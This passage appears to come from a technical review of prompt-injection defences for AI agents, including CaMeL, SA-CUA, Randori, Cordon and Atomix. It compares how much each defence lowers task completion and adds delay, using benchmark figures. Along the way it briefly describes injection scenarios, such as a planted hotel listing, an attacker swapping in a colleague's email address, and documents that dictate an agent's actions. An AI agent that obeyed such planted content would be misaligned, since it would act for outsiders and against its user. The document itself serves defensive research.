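A completely new language is harder for a model to write. In one of Garby and colleagues' examples, GPT-5.2 needed three attempts to write a valid factorial function in their LLMbda calculus, even with a summary of the syntax in its prompt. It would have had little trouble in ordinary Python. Their agent, Randori, still completed about as many banking tasks as CaMeL did without policies, but the two agents differ in too many ways to measure how many tasks were lost because of the language.

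### Planning before seeing the data

Peters-Gill and colleagues measured how much CaMeL's advance planning reduces task completion when several agents share each task. They tested five models on two benchmarks. From AssetOpsBench, which covers industrial equipment monitoring, they used the 112 tasks that an agent could complete. The other benchmark was their multi-agent version of AgentDojo, with 97 tasks.

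| Model | AssetOpsBench, without → with CaMeL | Multi-agent AgentDojo, without → with CaMeL |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5 | 88.4% → 67.0% | 91.1% → 84.4% |
| GPT-5.5 | 87.5% → 82.1% | 86.6% → 73.2% |
| GPT-4.1 | 81.2% → 64.3% | 78.4% → 38.1% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 75.9% → 55.4% | 76.3% → 42.3% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash-Lite | 64.3% → 20.5% | 27.8% → 13.4% |

Fable 5 refused many harmless AgentDojo tasks, apparently because they looked like a security test, so its AgentDojo figures cover only the 45 tasks without refusals. On all 97 tasks, restriction reduced its completion rate from 69.1% to 53.6%.

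These losses also include any failures caused by CaMeL's Python subset or by the quarantined model's mistakes. But Peters-Gill and colleagues examined the failures and found that most came from committing to a plan too early. In some tasks, it became clear that another action was needed only after a tool had returned its result. If a hotel responds that it needs a deposit within the hour, an agent that makes one call at a time can pay it. A program written in advance can pay it only if the model anticipated that a deposit might be needed.

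Other failures were harder to notice. Sometimes an agent couldn't find data for the requested machine or dates and returned data for similar ones, and the program that had requested the data kept running. A booking program could fail in the same way if a search for 3–6 June returned rooms for 4–6 June and the program never compared the dates.

Separating instructions from data between agents closed the security gap in the multi-agent version of CaMeL, but it lowered task completion on AssetOpsBench by another 3.2 points on average. On the AgentDojo version, Fable 5's completion rate did not fall, but GPT-4.1's fell another 13.4 points and Gemini 2.5 Pro's another 15.5. Peters-Gill and colleagues call the additional loss generally modest, which seems generous for GPT-4.1 and Gemini 2.5 Pro, since they ended up completing only about a quarter of the tasks.

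Stronger models seem to plan better in advance. On the AgentDojo version, Fable 5 kept 93% of its original score and GPT-5.5 kept 85%, while the other three models kept about half. The trend is less clear on AssetOpsBench, where Fable 5 lost 21.4 points and GPT-4.1 lost 16.9, although Fable 5 scored higher both with and without CaMeL.

### Tools have to describe what they return

All of these results depended on extra documentation, because the original tool descriptions in both benchmarks did not specify what the tools return. CaMeL's planner needs this information in advance, as Rai's code-writing agents did. If its code treats prices as numbers but the tool returns text, it may rank "1,050 EUR" as cheaper than "400 EUR", because "1" sorts before "4".

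Peters-Gill and colleagues therefore added a full description of the return format to every tool, which they found necessary for reasonable completion rates. CaMeL's developers had done the same for their own tests. Missing descriptions are a less serious problem for agents that write ordinary Python, because they can run a short program, inspect the result and write the next one.

Peters-Gill and colleagues regard the documentation as a small, one-time job for a developer. That is fair for a fixed set of tools, but if a personal assistant connects to new services every week, somebody would have to keep writing new descriptions and updating old ones whenever a service changed its format.

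### Planning for a screen the model cannot see

Advance planning is much harder for agents that use a computer through its screen. These agents normally look at a screenshot, click or type, and look again. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) adapts CaMeL to this setting but leaves out its policies. The planner never sees the screen, so it has to write instructions for every situation it can foresee, such as a cookie banner, a slow page or a browser that is already open.

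The screen-based plans averaged 213 lines and 40 branches, compared with 52 lines and about 4 branches for CaMeL's AgentDojo programs. A typical run left roughly half of the screen-based plan unused. Foerster and colleagues told the planner to observe the screen through a quarantined model, check for what it expected to find, and only then act. On 60 tasks from OSWorld, a benchmark of ordinary computer work, the agent completed 25 on a single attempt with this guidance and 4 without it.

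They report that the design keeps up to 57% of a frontier agent's performance. This figure comes from 109 OSWorld tasks, apparently the ones that an agent using Claude Sonnet 4.5 had solved without the defence. With the defence, the agent solved 62 of them in at least one of five attempts, and 31 (28%) on a single attempt. The single-attempt figure slightly understates the share of performance kept, because the undefended agent probably wouldn't have solved all 109 tasks again either.

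Pass@5 counts a task as completed if any of five attempts succeeds, whereas τ-bench's pass^k requires every attempt to succeed. Foerster and colleagues acknowledge that pass@5 is an upper bound, since reaching it requires someone to pick out the attempt that worked. The measure also suits a benchmark that resets after every attempt, because without a reset, a booking agent that carried out five plans could reserve five hotels.

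The study also suggests that planning without access to the data is a bigger problem than planning only once. It included a version based on FIDES, which calls its planner again before each action but hides untrusted results from it. With one attempt at each of the same 60 tasks, this version completed 20 and the CaMeL version completed 25. With five attempts, the FIDES version completed 40 and the CaMeL version completed 39. The FIDES version also used far more tokens.

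Seip, Markovinović and Hein (2026), in *Towards Safe Autonomy for Computer Use*, report much worse results for the screen-based CaMeL. With GPT-5.6-Luna as the planner, it completed 3 of 36 OSWorld tasks, while an undefended agent completed 21. On 99 browser tasks, CaMeL completed 19 and the undefended agent 91. In a typical failure on another set of tasks, the agent tried to click a GitHub link that was not clickable, and the whole run failed. An agent that could see the page might have typed the address instead. Seip and colleagues ran CaMeL as a baseline for their own system, with different models and prompts, so their figures are not directly comparable with those of Foerster and colleagues, but both sets of results show a large loss on single attempts.

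At each step, their own system, SA-CUA, shows the planner only parts of the screen that outsiders cannot have written. It finds these parts using the accessibility tree, the structured description of a screen that screen readers use. With GPT-5.6-Luna, SA-CUA completed 14 of the 36 OSWorld tasks and 49 of the 99 browser tasks, far better than CaMeL but still well below the undefended agent. It fell short partly because it also hid about 62% of the elements it could safely have shown. It also refuses to act on information it cannot verify, so its result reflects the effects of both its planning method and this policy.

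In these tests, the choice of planner affected how many tasks were completed, but a better planner didn't recover all the tasks lost to restriction. Of the nine planners that Foerster and colleagues compared, GPT-5 completed the most tasks, 12 of 17, and the weaker ones often left out fallback steps. In Seip and colleagues' tests, replacing Qwen3.8-27B with GPT-5.6-Luna raised CaMeL's score on the browser tasks from 9.1% to 19.2%, but its score on OSWorld stayed at 8.3%.

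### "Do what this document says"

Better planning helps when the model can foresee obstacles. Foerster and colleagues argue that many computer tasks depend less on what the agent finds than they appear to, because problems such as cookie banners recur. A model that knows about cookie banners can include a branch for them in its plan before seeing the page.

The request "do what this document says" is different because the plan itself is in the document. With the booking agent's seven tools, a document that lists five actions could describe any of

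7⁵ = 16,807

sequences of calls, even before anyone chooses the dates and hotels. A program can avoid listing them by calling whichever tools the document names, as CaMeL's program did in two banking runs, but that lets the document's author control the agent. As long as the planner cannot read the document, the agent has to fail the task or give up much of its protection, however capable the model is.

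Seip and colleagues accept this limit. Before SA-CUA starts, a classifier checks whether the user's request describes the necessary values precisely enough to verify them later. The classifier sends back requests such as "follow the instructions on screen" and asks the user for more detail.

The user doesn't have to know the answer in advance. For example, she may ask for a Python package that prints coloured text, and the agent may find the name `termcolor` in a forum post. Before it receives that name, the planner can predict one from its own knowledge, and ordinary code can then check whether the two match. Seip and colleagues call this *endorsement*. Garby and colleagues use the same term, but Seip and colleagues require a value to pass an independent check before the system trusts it.

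This doesn't work when the only evidence comes from the untrusted source. Seip and colleagues give the example of buying a laptop that meets a condition mentioned only in the seller's description. The planted hotel listing has the same problem, since the hotel may be the only source on whether its rooms face the sea.

### Being refused by a policy

Policies can block a task even when the model has written a correct program. Garby and colleagues tested this by running CaMeL three times on each of AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks, with and without its policies. They also cite a similar comparison from *Language-Based Agent Control*, whose system, TypeGuard, checks Haskell programs. *SPA* reports figures for ordinary AgentDojo tasks and for a version that spreads each task over several requests. All of these figures come from tests without attacks.

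| System and tasks | Completed without policies | Completed with policies | Share kept |
|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL with GPT-5.2, banking | 32 of 48 runs | 18 of 48 runs | 56% |
| CaMeL with MiMo-v2.5, banking | 34 of 48 runs | 18 of 48 runs | 53% |
| TypeGuard, Slack | 15 of 21 tasks | 8 of 21 tasks | 53% |
| SPA, AgentDojo | 53.0% | 29.0% | 55% |
| SPA, several requests | 62.5% | 35.3% | 56% |

The systems work differently, but each still completed slightly more than half of the tasks it had completed without policies. The results are probably similar because all of these tasks come from AgentDojo, where users often ask the agent to act on something an outsider could have written, such as a bill. An agent that works mainly with a company's own trusted records would presumably lose fewer tasks.

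For CaMeL's score of 18 out of 48, Garby and colleagues report a confidence interval of plus or minus 26.6 percentage points for both models. With 16 tasks and this average, the interval can be that wide only if each model completed six tasks in all three runs and never completed the other ten. Trying again would therefore not have helped, which is consistent with a fixed rule blocking the task.

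According to *SPA*, most of its losses came from plans that passed untrusted data to an action that required trusted data. Retrieving saved results was a smaller problem. When a later request needed a saved result, SPA retrieved it 95.4% of the time without the labels and 89.9% with them. SPA never revises a rejected plan, so a task counts as failed even if a small change would have made the plan acceptable.

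Some refusals are correct. Garby and colleagues cite the TypeGuard researchers' observation that many of the tasks "involve flows that no secure policy would admit". Refusing such a task still counts as a failure on a benchmark, although a bank might want its agent to refuse to pay a bill it could not verify. The TypeGuard researchers suggest asking the user to confirm these cases, which would recover some tasks but add approval requests that people may not read carefully.

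Randori always enforces its labels, but endorsement lets it complete some of these tasks without asking the user. It completed 36 of 48 banking runs with GPT-5.2, 36 with Qwen3.7-plus and 31 with MiMo-v2.5. When Garby and colleagues removed endorsement, completed runs fell to 30 with Qwen3.7-plus and 26 with MiMo-v2.5. Three of the 16 tasks depend on endorsement because they ask the agent to act on a file's contents.

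Garby and colleagues conclude that Randori matches CaMeL without policies, within confidence intervals. But the intervals extend about 20 points in each direction, so there could still be a fairly large difference. Endorsement also moves part of the decision from a fixed policy to the model that writes the program.

Restrictions can increase the number of completed tasks when an attacker is present. Seip and colleagues created 78 tasks in which the attacker substitutes one value for another, such as a colleague's email address. With GPT-5.6-Luna, the undefended agent completed 60.3% of them and SA-CUA completed 69.2%, because an agent that accepts the attacker's value usually fails the user's task too. With Qwen3.8-27B, however, SA-CUA completed slightly fewer than the undefended agent, 50.9% against 53.4%.

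There is little evidence that stronger models lose fewer tasks to a fixed policy. GPT-5.2 and MiMo-v2.5 completed different numbers of tasks without CaMeL's policies and the same number with them. Two models are a small sample, but the result is plausible because the policy checks where the data came from, and a better program doesn't change that. A stronger model could still help by finding a way to complete the task using only trusted data, if one exists, or by judging more carefully what to endorse.

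### Ordinary tasks under Cordon

Cordon, the transactional runtime, mostly avoids the first two problems. The model makes ordinary tool calls and can usually read each result before choosing the next step, so it doesn't need a new language or a complete plan. The agent could still fail tasks if the final check rejects legitimate work, or if it needs a real result from a call that Cordon is holding back.

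Chen and colleagues compared Cordon with a plain agent on subsets of two benchmarks. On τ-bench, the plain agent completed 87.5% of the tasks and Cordon 90.0%. On Terminal-Bench, a set of command-line tasks, both completed 100%.

These results show no sign of a large drop in completed tasks, but the subsets are too small to rule out a moderate one. The two τ-bench percentages require a set of at least 40 tasks, and with 40 they differ by one task. A score of 36 out of 40 is compatible with a true completion rate between about 77% and 96%. The perfect scores on Terminal-Bench are not much more informative, because tasks that both agents always complete may be too easy to reveal a difference. If Cordon lowered completion from 90% to 85%, a study would need nearly 700 separate runs of each version to have an 80% chance of detecting the drop.

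## What serialised execution costs

Serialising means forcing calls, transactions or agents to run one after another. An interpreter serialises tool calls when it finishes each one before starting the next. A runtime serialises agents when it makes one wait because another is using the same hotel reservation. An approval request stops a whole task until somebody answers. These delays range from a few milliseconds for a lock to hours when an approver is unavailable.

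Running everything one at a time is stricter than correctness requires. The work usually only needs to be serialisable, meaning that its result equals the result of some one-at-a-time order. Two agents that book trips for different customers can run at the same time, because the outcome is the same whichever goes first. In the booking example, the second agent's result matches neither order. If the booking finished first, the second agent would find a complete trip and could move all of it to 4 June. If the second agent went first, it would find no reservation to move. A hotel on 4 June with a flight on 3 June can come only from mixing the two agents' steps. A runtime therefore has to prevent that mixture, but it can let everything else overlap.

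### The longest chain of calls

Suppose each of the booking agent's seven calls takes two seconds. In sequence, they take 14 seconds. If the agent runs the three searches in parallel, followed by the three reservations in parallel and finally the email, they take 6 seconds.

No further parallelism can improve on 6 seconds, because the email waits for the reservations and the reservations wait for the searches. In general, if call *i* takes tᵢ seconds, the running time T of a program satisfies

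T ≥ the largest sum of tᵢ along any chain of dependent calls

The booking's longest chain has three calls, so parallel execution can make it at most 14/6 ≈ 2.3 times as fast. One slow call can reduce the gain a lot. If the flight search took 10 seconds, the total would be 22 seconds and the longest chain 14 seconds, so parallel execution could make the booking at most about 1.6 times as fast.

The faster schedule also leaves more bookings to cancel when one fails. If the flight reservation fails, a sequential program stops with only the hotel booked, while in a parallel one the agent may have to cancel the car as well. PopPy's cautious default makes the reservations in the order the model wrote them and takes 10 seconds, four more than the parallel schedule.

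### Parallel calls within a program

Quasar, the restricted language that starts a call as soon as its arguments are known, runs independent calls in parallel automatically. Mell and colleagues compared it with ordinary Python on the same programs:

| Benchmark | Tasks with calls that could run in parallel | Time saved on those tasks | Time saved overall |
|---|---|---|---|
| GQA | 49% | 37% | 18% |
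| AgentDojo | 38% | 54% | 27% |
| BrowseComp-Plus (80 tasks) | Not reported | Not reported | 93% |

On the first two benchmarks, most programs had nothing to run in parallel. BrowseComp-Plus programs sped up much more because they make many model calls, few of which depend on each other. A 93% cut in running time makes a program about 14 times as fast.

The AgentDojo figures are slightly inconsistent, since saving 54% on 38% of the tasks would save about 21% overall. The two percentages may cover different sets of tasks, because Mell and colleagues excluded programs that ran in 100 milliseconds or less in Python.

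They also recorded how long each call took and replayed the recording in both languages. This removes random variation from the comparison, but it assumes that 100 simultaneous requests are each as fast as one request alone. The gain would be smaller if the model provider limited how many requests a customer can make at once. The times also exclude writing the program, which takes the same time either way, so the saving is a smaller share of the user's total wait.

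The tests of PopPy, the compiler that Quasar adapts, used live calls to a model. Mell and colleagues collected 35 programs and found that each spent well under 1% of its time running its own Python code and the rest waiting for models. PopPy typically makes the Python code about 70 times slower, but this adds less time than overlapping the model calls saves, so the programs still finish sooner.

One of the programs solves arithmetic puzzles by asking a model to propose partial solutions, asking it again to score each one, and printing the scores. PopPy starts the scoring calls together but still prints the scores in order. It cut the running time from 271 seconds to 40, a 6.7-fold speedup.

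That was the best case, and the average speedup across all 35 programs was 1.8 times. The five programs that people wrote averaged 3.9 times, which implies about 1.6 times for the 30 that models wrote. Those 30 are closer to what an agent produces during a task. A programmer can still do better by arranging the parallel calls by hand, since PopPy was 17.2% slower than hand-written parallel versions of the five human-written programs.

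The idea is older than either system. *An LLM Compiler for Parallel Function Calling* (Kim, Moon and colleagues, 2024) reported speedups of up to 3.7 times over ReAct, a standard loop in which a model reasons and then makes one call at a time. It also reported accuracy gains of up to about 9%, but its system plans differently from ReAct, so the gains don't show that speed itself improves accuracy.

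### Working while a call is running

Even when calls depend on each other, the model may have useful work to do while it waits. In ordinary tool calling, it stops generating text until the tool returns. *Asynchronous LLM Function Calling* (Gim, Lee and Zhong, 2024) presents AsyncLM, which lets the model keep generating and interrupts it when a result arrives.

In *Concurrency without Model Changes*, Feng, Mao and colleagues (2026) achieve something similar with existing models and tools. Their system gives the model a placeholder for each unfinished result, and the model keeps working with the placeholder until it needs the real value. Coding tasks finished 1.4 times as fast with no loss of accuracy. This is mildly encouraging for transactional runtimes, which also give the model placeholders. But the placeholders in Feng et al.'s system soon turn into real results, whereas a staged reservation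 has no result until the commit.

An agent can also save time by guessing its next action and starting it early. *Speculative Actions* (Ye, Ahuja and colleagues, 2025) uses a small, fast model to predict what the main model will do next. The system ignores the result of the predicted action unless the main model chooses the same one. The small model guessed correctly up to 55% of the time, and waiting time fell by up to 20%. The saving is smaller than the accuracy because a correct guess saves only the time during which the two models' work overlaps.

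Guessing searches is much safer than guessing reservations. *Speculate with Memory* (2026), a later system of this kind, starts only read-only actions early and excludes writes with irreversible side effects. In the booking example, it could speed up the three searches but not the confirmation email. But a wrongly guessed search can still leak data through its search terms.

Transactions also let an agent try actions that have side effects before it knows whether they are right, because the runtime can discard the wrong ones. Mohammadi and colleagues used Atomix, their transactional runtime, to explore 2 to 16 alternative plans at once and commit only one. The abandoned plans left no lasting effects. Several simpler methods protected database records but had no special handling for email, so they sent one email for every abandoned plan. Serialising the plans would also have avoided those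 emails, but the agent would have had to try up to 16 plans in turn.

### Locks, optimistic checking and frontiers

When several agents share a resource, a runtime can keep their work serialisable in roughly three ways. It can lock the resource, so that other agents wait. It can use optimistic checking, which lets all agents proceed and, at commit, rejects any transaction whose data has changed since it was read. Or it can track unfinished earlier transactions and make a transaction wait only for those that touch the same resources. Atomix combines the last approach with a check for outdated reads.

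Atomix gives each read and effect an epoch, a number that shows its place in the order of events. For a transaction T, e(T) is the highest epoch of anything it read or changed, and R(T) is the set of resources involved. Each resource *r* also has a frontier. The frontier may reach epoch *e* only when every transaction that touches *r* and has an earlier epoch has either committed or aborted. T may commit only if

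frontier(r) ≥ e(T) for every r in R(T)

Suppose the booking has epoch 5 and touches the customer's hotel, flight and car reservations. The second agent's date change has epoch 6 and touches the same hotel reservation. A third agent's transaction has epoch 7 and concerns a different customer.

1. Nothing earlier is pending on the booking's three reservations, so their frontiers stand at 5 and the booking may commit when it is ready.
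2. The hotel's frontier can't reach 6 until the booking finishes, so the date change has to wait.
3. The third transaction shares nothing with the others. The frontiers of its own resources can reach 7, and it commits without waiting for either of them.
4. The booking commits, and the hotel's frontier moves to 6. The commit also changes the reservation's version number. If the second agent read the old version, Atomix aborts the date change and tries it again on the finished trip.

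The orchestrator, the program that coordinates the agents, has to move the frontiers correctly. When Mohammadi and colleagues made it move a frontier too early, all 200 test transactions committed out of order. When it never moved the frontier, all 200 were stuck. In practice, a hung agent can also leave transactions stuck, at least until the orchestrator stops waiting for it.

Atomix also relies on developers to describe which resources each tool touches. A description that is too broad makes unrelated work wait, but one that is too narrow is worse because Atomix then misses real conflicts. In a test with overly narrow descriptions, Atomix broke the rules of the task in 66 of 200 trials.

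### Four agents and one order

Mohammadi and colleagues compared these methods by giving four agents conflicting jobs on the same retail order, with some trying to cancel it and others trying to change its address. The researchers ran each method 100 times, with a short artificial pause in place of the model's thinking. They also gave agents separate orders, where no agent needed to wait.

| Method | Violations per run, same order | Average wait, same order | Average wait, separate orders (4 agents / 8 agents) |
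|---|---|---|---|
| No protection | 4.97 | 0 ms | 0 / 0 ms |
| Lock for each call | 4.91 | 0 ms | 0 / 0 ms |
| Lock for the whole workflow | 0 | 112 ms | 45 / 105 ms |
| Optimistic checking | 0 | 0 ms | 0 / 0 ms |
| Atomix | 0 | 0 ms | 0 / 0 ms |

Locking each call separately was barely better than no locking, because another agent could still change an order after the first agent had read it but before it wrote its update. Holding one lock for the whole workflow prevents this, but it also delays agents working on other orders.

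Optimistic checking avoids both problems by discarding the work behind rejected commits. Mohammadi and colleagues give two figures for rejections with four agents: 3,000 per 100 runs (30 per run) in one place and three per run in another. The lower figure seems more plausible, because it matches the number of conflicts that the unprotected agents committed when a real model did the planning. A database can repeat a rejected query in milliseconds, but an agent may have to call the model again to make a new plan.

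Atomix also retries transactions that have read outdated data, and its average wait of zero doesn't include this repeated work. In another test, Atomix completed 5.09 transactions per step when none of them overlapped and 1.66 when all of them did, compared with 1.00 for a single lock in both cases. Its advantage is therefore largest when agents mostly work on different things.

### Holding a lock while the model thinks

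A single lock makes agents wait much longer as their number grows, even when each agent's work is separate. Mohammadi and colleagues measured average waits of 564 milliseconds with 16 agents, 1,163 with 32 and 2,369 with 64. Atomix's separate frontiers kept the wait at zero in all three cases.

These waits follow a simple pattern. If *n* agents request a lock together and each holds it for a time *h*, the first waits for nothing, the second for *h*, the third for 2*h*, and so on. The average is

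(n − 1)h / 2

With *h* at 75 milliseconds, this gives 563, 1,163 and 2,363, almost exactly the measured values.

The formula also shows why agents wait much longer when each one holds the lock during a model call. The artificial pause in this test lasted 50 milliseconds, while a call to GPT-4o-mini, a small model from 2024, took about 700. If each of 64 agents held the lock for 700 milliseconds, they would wait an average of 22 seconds. If each held it while a model reasoned for 10 seconds, the average wait would be over five minutes.

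Mohammadi and colleagues confirmed the direction of this effect in a test with four agents, two shared orders and real calls to GPT-4o-mini. The agents waited 1,651 milliseconds per run with a lock on the whole workflow and 635 milliseconds with Atomix, so Atomix evidently still makes agents wait when they compete for an order. A designer could release the lock while the model generates a response, but the runtime would then have to check for changes before committing.

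Atomix's own bookkeeping is negligible by comparison. It adds about 8 microseconds to each step, and τ-bench tasks without injected faults took 164 seconds with Atomix and 171 without it.

### Cordon's running time

Chen and colleagues timed Cordon, which checks a whole task before committing it, on their 45 risky workflows. They ran each workflow without Cordon and then with it, using three preset ways of answering its approval requests.

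| Mode | Average time per task | Change | Model calls in total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Without Cordon | 25.55 s | – | 162 |
| Approve everything | 31.35 s | +22.7% | 119 |
| Reject risky transactions | 23.64 s | −7.5% | 125 |
| Mixed | 31.12 s | +21.8% | 127 |

Excluding the wait for approval, tasks took 24.6% to 27.9% less time with Cordon than without it. Cordon often stopped a dangerous run before the agent had made all its calls, so the shorter times don't show that transactions speed up an agent. Time fell most in workflows where a command tried to send out data derived from a secret. Workflows that deleted many files tended to be slower, because Cordon had to record the deletions, discard them and let the agent recover.

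The early stops mask the time Cordon adds. Excluding approval waits, its checking and record-keeping took 22% to 23% of the running time, or roughly four seconds per task. An ordinary task that ran to completion might well have a similar overhead with no early stop to offset it. Chen and colleagues ran Cordon on harmless tasks but reported only how many the agent completed, not how long it took.

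Waiting for approval added about 12 seconds per task when the policy approved everything. People are likely to be slower. Hossain and colleagues' volunteers took a median of 33 seconds to judge one request with the consequence ledger. Adding 33 seconds to Cordon's time excluding approval waits would give about 52 seconds, twice as long as the agent took without Cordon. Batching approvals reduces interruptions, but the task still can't finish before the last answer arrives.

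A slow approval can hold up other agents too. If the booking transaction stays open while the customer is at lunch, Atomix can't commit the second agent's change to the hotel reservation. Optimistic checking would let the second agent go ahead, but the customer might then return and approve a trip that has already changed, so the runtime would have to ask her again. Splitting the task into shorter transactions would free the reservation sooner, but the runtime would check less of the task together.

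### When delay makes a task fail

A slower agent can still complete the same tasks if it has no deadline and nothing changes while it waits. No published study seems to measure directly how many tasks agents fail because a runtime made their calls wait. Benchmarks such as τ-bench are poorly suited to measuring this because their databases change only when somebody calls a tool.

The closest result comes from Mohammadi and colleagues' test combining shared orders with random faults. At a 10% fault rate, a lock on the whole workflow produced a clean result in 81% of cases and Atomix in 84%, a difference that could be chance. The locked agents waited almost 100 milliseconds longer, but nothing in the test expired while they waited.

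Tasks in a changing environment give very different results. Zheng et al. (2025), in *Reflex First, Reflect Later*, point out that many simulators freeze while a model is thinking, which overstates how well slow planners perform. Several newer benchmarks keep the environment running during that time. In *Real-Time Reasoning Agents in Evolving Environments* (2025), an agent that planned carefully in simple games scored 0.92 with plenty of time and 0.05 under heavy time pressure. In one game, it steered a snake into a wall because the snake had moved while the agent was planning.

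*Action Windows Are Inherently Temporal* (2026) isolates the effect of delay by discounting the time an agent spends computing. On its robot tasks, the same GPT-6.1 Sol agent scored 0% when all of that time counted, 23.3% with a discount factor of 10 and 46.1% with a factor of 100. The agent often made a useful start and then ran out of time.

More reasoning can help or hurt when it uses up the available time. *Realtime-Bench* (2026) found that all six of its models did better with more reasoning when the clock was paused while they reasoned. When each token took a fixed amount of time, more reasoning reduced Claude's success rate from 44% to 30% but raised Kimi-K3's from 24% to 36%. Training under time limits may reduce the harm. In *Learning to Reason in Real-Time* (2026), agents trained without time limits did poorly under even mild time pressure, while those trained with them did much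 better.

The delays in these tests come from the model's reasoning, not from locks or approvals. Waiting for a lock should do similar harm, because a late command affects a moving robot the same way whatever caused the delay. But many agents do work that allows far more time than a game does. *Measuring Agents in Production* (2025) found that deployed agents most commonly have minutes to respond, and only 5 of its 20 detailed case studies needed real-time responses. Some of the agents process requests hourly or overnight.

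The booking falls between these extremes, because the last seat on a flight can sell at any time. Suppose the chance of losing it is 1% each minute. The eight seconds that parallel calls save would reduce the chance of losing the seat by about 0.1 percentage points, and a 33-second approval would add about half a point. If the approval request arrived at night and the customer answered eight hours later, the seat would almost certainly be gone.
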